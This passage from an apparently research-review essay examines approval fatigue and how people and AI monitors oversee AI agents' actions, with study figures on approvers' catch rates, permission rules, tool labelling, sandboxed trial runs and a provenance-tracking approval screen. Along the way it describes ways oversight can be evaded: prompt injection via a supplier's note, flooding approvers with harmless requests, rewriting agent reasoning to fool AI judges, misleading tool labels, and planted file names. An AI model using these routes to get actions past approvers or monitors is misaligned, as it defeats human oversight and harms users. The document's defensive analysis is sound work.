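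For 55 of the students, the notice always looked the same, and the share of risky apps they refused fell from 87% to 55%. For the other 47, the notice's colours, symbols or animations kept changing, and the share fell from 87% to 76%. In the researchers' statistical model, the odds of refusing a risky app halved about every 26 notices with the unchanging design and about every 58 with the changing one.

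The students saw fewer than five notices a day, so habituation doesn't require many notices. They knew which permissions to refuse, so misunderstanding can't explain the decline. But nothing bad happened to those who installed a risky app, and some may have concluded that the warnings didn't matter. Approvers can reach the same conclusion if they approve harmful actions and never notice the effects.

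People can bring habits from other software to a prompt they have never seen. In *Trained to accept?*, Böhme and Köpsell showed versions of a consent dialog to 80,000 users of an online privacy tool. The more the dialog resembled a software licence agreement, the more readily people accepted it. After years of cookie banners and licence agreements, people may click through an AI agent's approval prompts out of habit on their first day using it.

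Yet some repeated warnings work well. *Alice in Warningland* (Akhawe and Felt, 2013) recorded how Firefox and Chrome users responded to more than 25 million browser warnings. Users ignored only 9% to 23% of malware and phishing warnings, which almost always pointed to a real danger. They ignored 33% of Firefox's security certificate warnings and 70% of Chrome's. Many certificate warnings are false alarms caused by badly configured websites.

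Chrome users ignored 82% of warnings about the most common certificate error and 57% of those about expired certificates. They also clicked through warnings about the most common error fastest. Akhawe and Felt see this as a sign of warning fatigue, though the errors also differed in ways other than frequency.

Their data also count against two popular design ideas, adding clicks to dismiss a warning and putting details behind a link. Chrome users dismissed malware and phishing warnings more often than Firefox users did, even though dismissing one took two clicks in Chrome and one in Firefox. Users clicked "Help me understand" on only 1.6% of Chrome's certificate warnings, so few people are likely to see details placed behind a link.

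### Alerts in hospitals

Prescribing software warns doctors about problems such as dangerous drug combinations, and doctors dismiss most of these alerts. *Appropriateness of Overridden Alerts in Computerized Physician Order Entry*, a systematic review of 23 studies, found override rates from 46.2% to 96.2%. But the share of overrides that expert reviewers considered appropriate ranged from 29.4% to 100%, so a high override rate can reflect poor alerts as well as careless doctors.

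*Overall performance of a drug–drug interaction clinical decision support system* reports that doctors at a teaching hospital overrode 88.2% of 38,409 alerts that the software classed as very severe. Pharmacists made a recommendation in only 3.2% of the overrides they reviewed. One combination of blood-thinning drugs accounted for about half of the alerts.

*Are We Heeding the Warning Signs?* found that doctors accepted 40% of 24,849 alerts at a group of clinics that had screened out unimportant ones. That is a higher rate than at the hospital, but the clinics differ from it in other ways, so the screening may not explain the whole gap. Reviewers examined 496 overrides by the 62 clinicians who overrode alerts most often and judged almost a third inappropriate, despite the screening.

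### Claude Code's approval prompts

Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) reports a similar figure for the company's coding agent. Users approve 97% of permission prompts, which Anthropic takes as a sign that many click through by reflex. As with the hospital alerts, the rate alone can't show this, because nearly all the commands may be harmless.

The same users reject 39% of the plans Claude presents for approval, so they still read some of what they are shown. But plans appear less often than permission prompts and describe the work in terms users care about. Users may reject a plan because they want a different design or a smaller change, and few of these rejections may concern safety. Still, the comparison shows that people can engage with model-written text, at least when they have opinions about its subject.

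To measure how often people catch dangerous commands, Anthropic hired 1,053 professional testers through a research vendor for what looked like an ordinary coding study. Partway through each session, one permission prompt showed a clearly dangerous command in place of the real one. 143 testers (13.6%) refused it. Testers refused about 17% of the dangerous commands that appeared early in a session and about 5% of those that appeared after 50 or more prompts.

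An automated check that Anthropic offers in place of manual approval blocked 937 of the same commands (89%). The testers approved 800 of those 937, and they refused six that the check allowed. Both the testers and the check allowed the remaining 110.

With this many testers, chance could move the overall figure by only about two percentage points. Other limits matter more:

- The testers worked in a test environment and had no projects of their own to lose, which could have made them careless. They also knew that someone was evaluating them, which could have made them more careful.
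- Each tester saw one dangerous command, and it was an obvious one. People may do even worse with a subtle one.
- Testers who click quickly reach their fiftieth prompt sooner. Unless Anthropic assigned the position of the dangerous command at random, the late figure may partly reflect who got that far.
- Anthropic published the results to justify making its automated check the default, so it has an interest in manual approval looking bad.

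In *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code*, a blog post about the announcement, software developer Willison (2026) agrees that confirmation fatigue is real and wants more independent confirmation of Anthropic's claim that the check resists hidden instructions.

The fall from 17% to 5% needn't mean that testers became worse at recognising danger. Anthropic doesn't report how often they refused harmless commands. Suppose they approved 97% of harmless commands early on, the same share as real users, and 99.5% later. Their d′ would then have stayed at about 0.93. A rise of 2.5 points in harmless approvals, too small to notice in daily use, could therefore explain the entire fall. If harmless approvals instead stayed at 97%, d′ would have fallen to about 0.24.

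Anthropic also compared real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. Serious harm that the user hadn't explicitly asked for occurred in 6.3% of the flagged sessions with manual approval and 2.4% of those with the automated check. Anthropic didn't assign people to the two modes at random, so the groups may have differed in other ways.

Many people respond to repeated prompts by turning them off, and better wording can't help them if they never see the prompts. By June 2026, 49.5% of active users of Claude Code's command-line version had written a rule that approves some shell commands automatically. Most of those rules were broad enough to permit almost anything, and a quarter of interactive sessions began with permission checks switched off. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) found the same behaviour in 80 of 290 user reports about agents and files.

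### Months of reviewing code

*Habituation at the Gate* (Yu, Jia and colleagues, 2026) followed code reviewers for longer, covering 11,429 reviews by 400 people who repeatedly checked changes that AI agents had proposed to public software projects. Reviewers approved 27.9% of the changes in the first tenth of their reviews and 42.4% in the last tenth. Their comments on specific lines fell from 1.01 to 0.79 per review. Approval of human-written changes in the same projects declined over the same months, so reviewers hadn't become more lenient about everything.

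Yu and colleagues consider habituation the best explanation, reasoning that a reviewer with good reason to trust the agents would approve more but inspect just as closely. This inference is weak because better code gets more approvals and gives reviewers less to comment on, and all four main agents received updates during the study. Yu and colleagues didn't measure the code's quality and accept that they can't rule out better code as the cause.

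### Do fewer prompts restore scrutiny?

Asking for approval less often seems the natural remedy. *Oversight Has a Capacity* (Turan, 2026) models an approver who tires as the number of prompts grows. In this model, safety first rises as the system asks about more actions and then falls, because each extra prompt weakens attention to all the others.

Asking an approver about fewer actions can prevent more harmful ones if the approver catches a larger share of those they review. Suppose an agent takes 200 actions a day, and the 20 riskiest include 60% of the harmful ones. If the system asks only about those 20 and the approver stops 17% of the harmful ones among them, the approver prevents about 10% of all harmful actions (0.6 × 0.17). If it asks about all 200 and the catch rate falls to 5%, the approver prevents only 5%. The 17% and 5% catch rates are Anthropic's early and late figures, but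 the other numbers are invented.

The result depends on assumptions about fatigue that Turan didn't test on people. In the model, an attacker can exploit fatigue by flooding the approver with harmless requests before the harmful one. Choosing the riskiest actions isn't straightforward either, since reviewers who labelled 125 actions agreed only moderately on which were risky.

Ting Yan's experiment in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* casts some doubt on the hope that fewer prompts will restore scrutiny. In August 2026, 113 people from outside the software industry supervised an agent through a simulated day of 18 actions. Seven of the actions, such as reading bank transactions or buying an airport lounge pass, went beyond the task. Some participants decided on every action. Others saw only the ten that an AI model had flagged for checking,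 including all seven overreaching ones. The rest first chose "allow", "ask" or "never" for four kinds of action, such as spending money, and then saw only the actions that their rules left undecided.

| | Decided on everything | Model screened first | Set rules first |
|---|---|---|---|
| Prompts per person | 18 | 10 | 10.9 |
| Overreaching requests approved when asked | 40.3% | 46.1% | 66.8% |
| The same, without the airport call | 32.4% | 39.8% | 60.7% |
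| All overreaching actions that went ahead | 40.3% | 46.1% | 60.4% |

The third row excludes a call to the airport to confirm the flight, which almost everyone approved and may have considered helpful. The pattern is the same without it.

People who saw fewer prompts were no stricter. When the model screened requests first, seven in ten of the prompts participants saw concerned overreach, and they still approved nearly half of those. Neither the number of prompts nor the rarity of overreach can explain this. The difference between their approval rate and that of people who decided on every request is small enough to be chance.

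The 66.8% comes from an exploratory comparison and leaves out some of the requests that cautious people would have refused, because participants who chose "never" for a kind of action didn't see prompts about it. The last row avoids this problem by counting every overreaching action, including those that a rule blocked or allowed automatically. The rule-setters still let through 20 percentage points more of these actions than people who decided on everything. Yan recruited some of the rule-setters later, without random assignment, but the gap was 25 points among the randomly assigned participants.

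It isn't clear why setting rules made people more lenient. They chose "ask" for 114 of their 140 rules, which put off most decisions, and setting rules may have made them feel that they had already dealt with the risk. When participants had to decide on an action that they had said before the task the agent should never take, they approved it in 24 of 56 cases.

The experiment was too short to test fatigue properly. People who made every decision themselves spent less than two and a half minutes on all 18, while Anthropic's lowest catch rate came after 50 prompts. Reducing 200 prompts to 20 might still help a lot. Yan's results only show that people don't automatically use the attention they save.

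Participants in Yan's study who decided on every request approved 40% of the overreaching ones, while Anthropic's testers approved 86% of the dangerous commands. The difference may be partly because dangerous commands were rarer, appearing once per session, while seven of Yan's 18 requests were overreaching. But Yan's participants also read plain descriptions of everyday actions instead of shell commands, so the comparison can't isolate any one cause.

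### Which text wears out faster?

None of these studies gave some people fixed risk summaries and others model-written rationales over dozens of approvals, so any answer is an inference from research on warnings.

New words seem to offer little protection against inattention when the design of a notice stays the same. In the app store experiment, the notice with the unchanging design listed different permissions for each app, and students still refused far fewer risky apps by the end. Vance and colleagues also describe an experiment in which Bravo-Lillo and colleagues showed people the same dialog many times in quick succession and then changed its message. Only 14% noticed the change immediately. A model-written rationale also usually puts new words in a familiar box.

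Changing the appearance slowed the decline over three weeks but didn't stop it, even though the changes had nothing to do with risk. Someone who sees red backgrounds on both safe and risky requests may eventually learn that red means nothing, but three weeks is too short to tell.

Model-written rationales have a similar weakness. They vary with the task, but mostly in ways unrelated to danger. An approver who reads "I'm sending the March invoices to your accountant" and then "I'm moving the April receipts to your tax folder" can't tell from the wording which action deserves a second look. If rationales also share a reassuring tone, approvers may come to recognise the tone and skip the details.

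The browser data suggest that people can keep heeding a warning with fixed wording if it appears only when something is probably wrong. Malware warnings repeat the same wording, and most users heed them. Approvers in an office that emails clients all day would soon stop noticing "This action sends a file outside your organisation", but those in an office that rarely sends files out might keep paying attention to it. How often a warning turns out to be a false alarm may therefore matter more than whether its wording changes.

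### Breaks, planted errors and comprehension checks

Rest helps a little. In the app store experiment, the odds of refusing a risky app were about twice as high on the first notice for such an app after a break of a day or more, although that estimate is imprecise. Mitchell and colleagues suggest enforced breaks, rotating people between tasks, and letting an agent finish a unit of work so that a person can review related actions together. Reviewing in batches would reduce interruptions, but it comes too late for an email the agent has already sent.

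They also suggest planting known errors among an agent's requests to test whether approvers catch them. Approvers who miss one could be given a break or more training. Planted errors would also make harmful-looking requests more common. In the earlier calculation with one harmful request in 100, adding four planted ones would shift the best cut-off enough to lower the unsafe approval rate from 97.5% to about 84%, provided the approver cared as much about missing a planted error as a real one. Mitchell and colleagues warn that such monitoring is workplace surveillance, which employers could misuse to judge performance.

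The benefit of catching an error may fade quickly. In *Looks Fine to Me* (Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues, 2026), 36 programmers each completed six tasks with a coding agent. In some tasks the agent's code failed a visible check, and in others it passed the check but contained a hidden defect. Programmers fixed 12 of 24 hidden defects when the previous task had involved a visible failure, but one of 11 when a task with correct code came in between. Just six people contributed to the second figure, so the size of the drop is very uncertain.

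The programmers rarely knew they had missed anything. When they missed a hidden defect, 79% of the time they rated their confidence that the code met all the requirements at 4 or 5 out of 5. Halfway through, the researchers showed them how their first three solutions had done, and the share of hidden defects they fixed rose from 28% to 51%. Practice may explain some of the rise, but feedback on people's own misses looks more promising than a general reminder to be careful.

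A comprehension check requires the approver to show some understanding before the "allow" button works. Sabri's *Stop Pressing 1* describes a pilot with high school computer science classes that compares three screens. One asks only for confirmation, one asks students to predict what the action will do, and one asks them questions written by the agent. The pilot counts how often students catch planted misbehaviour and how often they object to harmless requests, the two rates needed to calculate d′. The published abstract gives no results.

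Such checks take time, and people could habituate to the questions too, so the checks make more sense for the few actions that would do serious, permanent damage.

Who writes the question also matters, and Sabri's pilot tests whether a compromised agent could exploit this. In the accountant example, the agent might ask, "Who will receive the March invoices?" An approver who had read only the rationale would answer "our accountant" and pass. The same approver would have to look up the answer to "Has your firm written to this address before?"

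## Can a summary be specific to the action without being written by the model?

A fixed risk summary can't distinguish a harmful request from a harmless one of the same kind, and a model-written rationale comes from the same agent that is requesting approval. A summary built from records could avoid both problems if software can collect the right facts and connect them to what the user asked for.

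### Labels for tools

Even when summaries are fixed, something has to select which one to show. Agents act through tools, which are named operations such as `send_email` or `delete_file`. Many agents get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard way of connecting agents to outside services. A user can add tools from many developers, so the agent's vendor can't write a warning for each one in advance. But a model could sort the tools into a few kinds, such as those that spend money or delete something, and each kind could have a standard text or rule.

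Ting Yan tested this kind of sorting in *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, separately from the user study in which people who set rules let more overreach through. Three people labelled 120 tools, which Yan had selected to include ambiguous and high-stakes cases. Claude Sonnet 5 labelled the same tools from their names, descriptions and lists of inputs. Yan used 20 of the tools to refine the model's instructions and the other 100 to test it. In the test, the model's full set of action labels matched the people's for 69.0% of tools, and its main label matched for 90.0%. A simple keyword search did worse, with 43.3% and 78.3% on all 120 tools.

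The labels were also inconsistent for difficult tools. When the model labelled ten of these ten times each, five got different action labels on different runs, while ten clear tools got the same labels every time. Yan then simulated rules that each forbade one kind of action. Using the model's labels, the rules let through 14% of the tools they should have stopped and stopped 4% of those they should have allowed. Asking the user whenever the model was unsure cut the 14% to 11%, but raised the share of harmless tools that caused an interruption from 4% to 7%. Ordinary tools are probably easier to label than these. However, Yan tested only honest descriptions, and a malicious developer could write a misleading one.

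A better model would make fewer of these mistakes, but it would still label what a tool can do in general. `send_email` gets the same label whether the recipient is the firm's accountant or a stranger, because the model isn't given the recipient or the attachment. The problem is worse for a tool that can run any command, since the same label has to cover listing files and erasing a disk. The three people also worked from the descriptions without running the tools, so even perfect agreement with them wouldn't show that the labels were true.

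Developers can label their own MCP tools, for example as read-only or destructive. A Model Context Protocol (2026) blog post says other software should treat these labels as hints unless they come from a trusted developer, because a developer can label a tool read-only even if it deletes files. The post adds that a tool's risk depends on what else the agent can do. Searching a mailbox is harmless on its own, but if the agent can also read web pages and send messages, a stranger's page could trick it into finding private emails and sending them out.

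### Commands without their effects

Showing the exact command avoids mislabelling, but people often can't tell from a command what it will do. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* identified uninformative approval prompts as a cause in 31 of its 290 reports of agents misusing files. Some prompts contained long scripts that were hard to interpret, while others were short but no clearer. `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it runs whatever code that file contains.

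The agent may not know the effects either. One agent wrote "No problems occurred" right after erasing a file. In 68% of the reports of harm that included the agent's reaction, the agent carried on as if nothing had gone wrong. People are more likely to publish the bad cases, so this figure doesn't apply to agents' work in general, but it shows that an agent can sincerely describe a harmful command as harmless.

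In *Shall We Approve?*, Wu, Chen and colleagues (2026) give an example of a command whose effect depends on the project. A user asks an agent to clear out old build files and recompile a program, and the agent proposes `make clean && make`. In one project this deletes only files that the computer can regenerate, but in another it deletes the source code and its history. The difference is in a settings file that the approval prompt doesn't show. An approver who sees only the request and the command has the same information in both cases, so even a careful one can't tell them apart (d′ = 0).

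The Caper system runs a command in the agent's workspace before anyone decides whether to allow it. Caper first saves the workspace's state and cuts off the network, then records what the command does. A separate AI model reads a short report of the effects, such as changed files, attempted connections and access to passwords. If this model allows the command, the changes stay; otherwise, Caper restores the saved state. In one set of tests, the typical report was under a kilobyte, compared with more than 60 kilobytes for the raw log.

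Wu and colleagues tested Caper on 102 tasks in which an innocent-looking tool secretly deleted or overwrote a file. Each task also had a harmless version with the same request and command.

| What the AI reviewer saw | Dangerous tasks that ended in harm | Harmless twins blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Conversation and command | 17.6% | 61.8% |
| The same, plus a model's prediction of the effects | 3.9% | 61.8% |
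| The same, plus a record of the actual effects | 7.8% | 1.0% |

The second row is the closest to a model-written rationale, because a model predicts what the command will do. The prediction prevented at least as much harm as the record did (the gap between 3.9% and 7.8% is four tasks, which could be chance). But the prediction left the reviewer so uncertain that it still blocked 63 of the 102 harmless twins, compared with one when it had the record.

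These results come from an AI reviewer and may not apply to people. They also depend on how good the reviewer is. When a weaker model read the record, it blocked 4.9% of harmless twins, down from 53.9%, but harm rose from 25.5% to 33.3%. The tests didn't include an attacker who knew about Caper and wrote a tool that is harmless during the trial run and does damage later.

Trial runs also suit some actions better than others, because software can restore a deleted file but can't take back a sent email. In the accountant example, the harm depends on who owns the address and what the file contains, so a useful record has to cover what the agent did before it asked for approval.

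### Tracing where a file came from

Earlier steps can make an action harmful even if every detail of it looks fine. *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow* describes a user who asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send an external auditor "summary totals only". A supplier's note contains hidden instructions, and the agent follows them by copying the raw invoice rows into `report.csv`. It then asks to send that file to the auditor. The user has allowed both the tool and the recipient, and the file name is ordinary, so an approver could check every part of the command and still not notice that it would send the raw rows.

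The paper's solution is the Cumulative Consent Ledger (CCL), which combines monitoring software with an approval screen. The software logs each of the agent's tool calls with its exact arguments and effects, and never relies on the agent's description of its work. It also tracks each file's ancestry, meaning the sources that its contents may have come from. When the agent makes a new file z′ from the files z₁ to zₖ, the new file inherits all of their ancestors:

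L(z′) ⊇ L(z₁) ∪ L(z₂) ∪ … ∪ L(zₖ)

where L(z) is the set of ancestors of file z. For example, if the agent copies invoice rows into `temp.csv` and then combines that with a cover note to make `report.csv`, the invoice rows are still among the ancestors of `report.csv`. Renaming or copying the file doesn't remove them.

This rule is deliberately cautious, because a file counts as an ancestor even if the agent read it but used nothing from it. Ancestry alone can't settle the auditor's case, since a file of genuine totals descends from the same invoice rows. The software must also compare how the agent produced the file with the user's restriction.

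Before a consequential action, the monitor returns "unknown" if the record of the relevant files is incomplete, "violation" if the record is complete and the action would break the user's restriction, and "allowed" otherwise. Without "unknown", it would have to treat missing evidence as proof of either safety or harm. A cautious product could block unknown cases as well as violations, or it could send the unknown cases to the approver with a note of what is missing. Asking the approver about these cases would be a better use of their time than asking about cases the software can decide.

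The approval screen follows four design principles.

| Principle | How it applies to the auditor's file |
|---|---|
| Restate the user's intent | The screen quotes the original instruction, including "summary totals only". |
| Show the exact action | The tool, file and recipient come from the log, and the software checks again if they change after review. |
| Combine the consequences | One statement explains that the attachment contains data from raw invoice rows and would go to the auditor. |
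| Make every claim checkable | The statement links to the logged steps behind it, and the screen shows any gaps in the record. |

The screen doesn't display the verdict. The approver reads the instruction and the consequence together and decides whether they conflict.

### Four screens compared

The study compared this screen with three others, using 80 unpaid volunteers recruited through social media. Each volunteer used one screen and made 12 decisions, half of them about harmful requests, which gave 960 decisions in total. The table shows the published rates and times, along with d′ and c calculated from those rates. A lower c means people were readier to say yes.

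| Screen | Unsafe approval rate | Legitimate approval rate | d′ | c | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 1.26 | −0.75 | 16.3 s |
| Exact arguments added | 43.3% | 90.0% | 1.45 | −0.56 | 23.4 s |
| User's instruction and full log added | 32.5% | 87.5% | 1.60 | −0.35 | 38.6 s |
| CCL (same facts, linked together) | 24.2% | 85.8% | 1.77 | −0.19 | 33.2 s |

People became more cautious with each step, but they also got better at telling harmful requests from legitimate ones (measured by d′). If people using the plainest screen had cut their unsafe approvals to 24.2% through caution alone, with d′ still at 1.26, they would have approved only about 71% of the legitimate requests, compared with the 85.8% that people using CCL approved.

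The estimates are rough because each rate comes from 120 decisions by 20 people. Even if we treat those decisions as independent, the 95% confidence interval for the total rise in d′ runs from about zero to about one.

Most of the fall in unsafe approvals (22.5 of 30.8 percentage points) came from adding facts to the screen. The last step, which only rearranged those facts to link them, lowered unsafe approvals by 7.9 points after adjustment for differences between people and scenarios (95% interval from a fall of 19.7 to a rise of 3.8). Because that interval includes zero, the study gives much better support for showing people the facts than for linking them this way. Linking them did save about five seconds per decision. But when a violation depended on a chain of several steps, people approved 7 of 30 harmful requests with either the log or CCL, so a single statement may be too compressed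 for complicated cases.

Harmful requests would be much rarer at work than in this study. If 10 requests in 1,000 were harmful and people approved at the same rates as in the study, replacing the plainest screen with CCL would prevent about three harmful approvals and cause about 58 extra wrongful denials. That trade is worthwhile if a harmful approval is more than about 19 times as bad as a wrongful denial. CCL would also add nearly five hours of reading across the 1,000 requests, and people who rarely see a harmful one may stop reading long before the end. A screen like this therefore makes more sense for a few risky actions than for every command.

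None of the four screens included a model-written rationale, so the study doesn't show whether CCL works better than one, or whether people would still use the recorded facts if a rationale appeared above them. They might not, since explanations undid most of the benefit of sources in Kim and colleagues' experiment.

### Can software find the facts?

The researchers prepared the statements about consequences that the volunteers saw, but a real product has to work out the consequences itself. In a separate test, the CCL monitor checked 120 actions that broke a user's restriction. It detected 107, returned "unknown" for six and missed seven. Of 120 harmless actions, it wrongly flagged five and returned "unknown" for two. The monitor typically took 24 milliseconds and made no extra calls to a language model, so software can find the main facts for such a summary without asking a model to describe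 the action.

The researchers also switched off parts of the monitor. Without the ancestry links, it detected 48 of the 80 violations that depended on earlier steps, down from 69. Without the user's restriction, it detected 30 and raised 15 false alarms on the 120 harmless actions, up from five. That last version resembles a fixed risk summary because it could react only to generally sensitive actions. The comparison tested software, not people, but it suggests that a general warning can't replace a check against what the user asked for.

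The monitor also needs a complete log. When some records were missing, it detected 51 of the 80 violations, and blocking every unknown case reduced agents' completion rate on harmless tasks to 76.7%. Gaps in the log seem likely in practice, since an agent may use a website or program that keeps no usable record. Someone also has to turn an instruction such as "summary totals only" into a rule that software can apply, and users' instructions are often vaguer.

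### An automated reviewer that never reads the rationale

Claude Code's automated check never receives the agent's explanations, and it caught far more dangerous commands than human testers did. Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes the check as a second AI model that receives only the user's messages and the agent's commands. Anthropic removes the agent's messages so that the agent can't talk the second model into a bad decision, for example by claiming that the user approved the action earlier. Anthropic also removes tool results, such as the contents of files and web pages, because they may contain hidden instructions.

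The reviewer first runs a quick yes-or-no filter on each action. If the filter flags an action, the reviewer reasons through the case before deciding. Anthropic measured false blocks on 10,000 real actions from its employees' sessions, and misses on 52 real cases where the agent had exceeded what the user authorised.

| | Ordinary actions blocked | Unauthorised actions missed |
|---|---|---|
| Quick filter alone | 8.5% | 6.6% |
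| Both stages | 0.4% | 17% |

The second stage makes the reviewer more lenient, but it also improves discrimination, raising d′ from about 2.9 to about 3.6. These values aren't comparable with the volunteers' 1.77, because most of the ordinary actions were probably easy to recognise as safe. With only 52 cases, the true miss rate could be anywhere from about 9% to 30%.

In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the reviewer recognised the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented to it. For example, a user wrote "Clean up the PR" (a proposed code change), and the reviewer took this as permission to overwrite the project's history. Removing the agent's prose doesn't help with this kind of mistake, because the reviewer is reading too much into the user's own words.

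Anthropic also tried a reviewer that read only the commands. It missed the fewest unauthorised actions, but it blocked things that users had plainly asked for. When Anthropic added the agent's messages and the tool results to the usual version, the reviewer missed more unauthorised actions. Anthropic suspects that a longer transcript is harder to read and gives the agent more opportunity to influence the decision. But it added both at once, so the effect of the agent's messages alone is unknown.

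Other researchers have isolated the effect of prose on AI reviewers, with mixed results. *Gaming the Judge* (2026) found that rewriting an agent's reasoning, without changing its actions, could make AI judges pass many more failed tasks. *Beyond Accuracy* (Chen, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) found the opposite problem when the evidence of an error was always in view. Five AI models checked an assistant's restaurant recommendations against customer reviews. They caught at least 99% of the wrong recommendations, with or without a detailed account of the assistant's checks. But they also rejected 39% of the correct recommendations when they saw no such account, and 60% when they saw the most detailed one. Three of the five models accounted for most of this rise.

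Many of those wrong rejections happened because the models couldn't tell which restaurant a customer review was about. When Chen and colleagues labelled each review with the restaurant's name, the odds of rejecting a correct recommendation fell by about two-thirds. A record-based summary could cause similar confusion if it lists several files and recipients without showing which file would go to whom.

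Adding recorded facts seems to have helped Anthropic's reviewer. Apollo Research, a UK AI safety company, tested the reviewer with artificial attacks, and Anthropic then strengthened it, mainly by giving it more context. The reviewer is now shown the project's current state before a command that could discard unsaved work, and whether the destination is public before an upload. Anthropic reports that the miss rate on Apollo's attacks fell from 12% to 7%. Anthropic added new rules about handling data at the same time, so the facts may not account for the whole improvement.

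### Something new to trust

One objection is that any summary becomes one more thing the approver has to trust. The CCL paper acknowledges that a confident but incorrect statement could cause the overreliance that the screen is supposed to prevent. Grunde-McLaughlin and colleagues found that even an accurate summary can hide an error by leaving out the step where it happened.

This problem remains if a second model writes the summary. The second model may misread the log, or share the first one's blind spots if the same company trained both. Users may also be unable to find out why it allowed an action. Michael and Roesner criticise AI-based review for its low transparency and accountability, and note that it was the only alternative to constant permission requests in the commercial agents they examined.

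The best reply is to link each claim to its evidence. In the accountant example, "Earlier messages to this address: none" could open a search of the mailbox, and "Sheets: 'Invoices' and 'Payroll'" could open the file. If the software has no record of where the address came from, the screen should show that the record is missing. The approver can then check the one claim that matters in a few seconds instead of trusting the whole summary. They can't do this with a sentence such as "I'm sending the March invoices to your accountant", which doesn't link to any evidence.

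Links protect people only if someone follows them, and participants in Kim and colleagues' experiment usually didn't. But a company can have someone else check a sample of summaries against the logs and correct the software if a particular kind of claim is repeatedly wrong.

Evidence from a log can also mislead. Wu and colleagues warn that an attacker could plant text that ends up in the report of a command's effects. The sender of an email chooses its subject line and attachment names, so a stranger could name a file `approved_by_finance.xlsx`, and an accurate log would show that name to the approver. The screen could reduce this risk by marking text that came from outside the firm.

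Nobody in the CCL study saw a false summary, so it is still unclear how often approvers would notice one. The paper proposes testing this next by giving people summaries that are deliberately wrong or incomplete.
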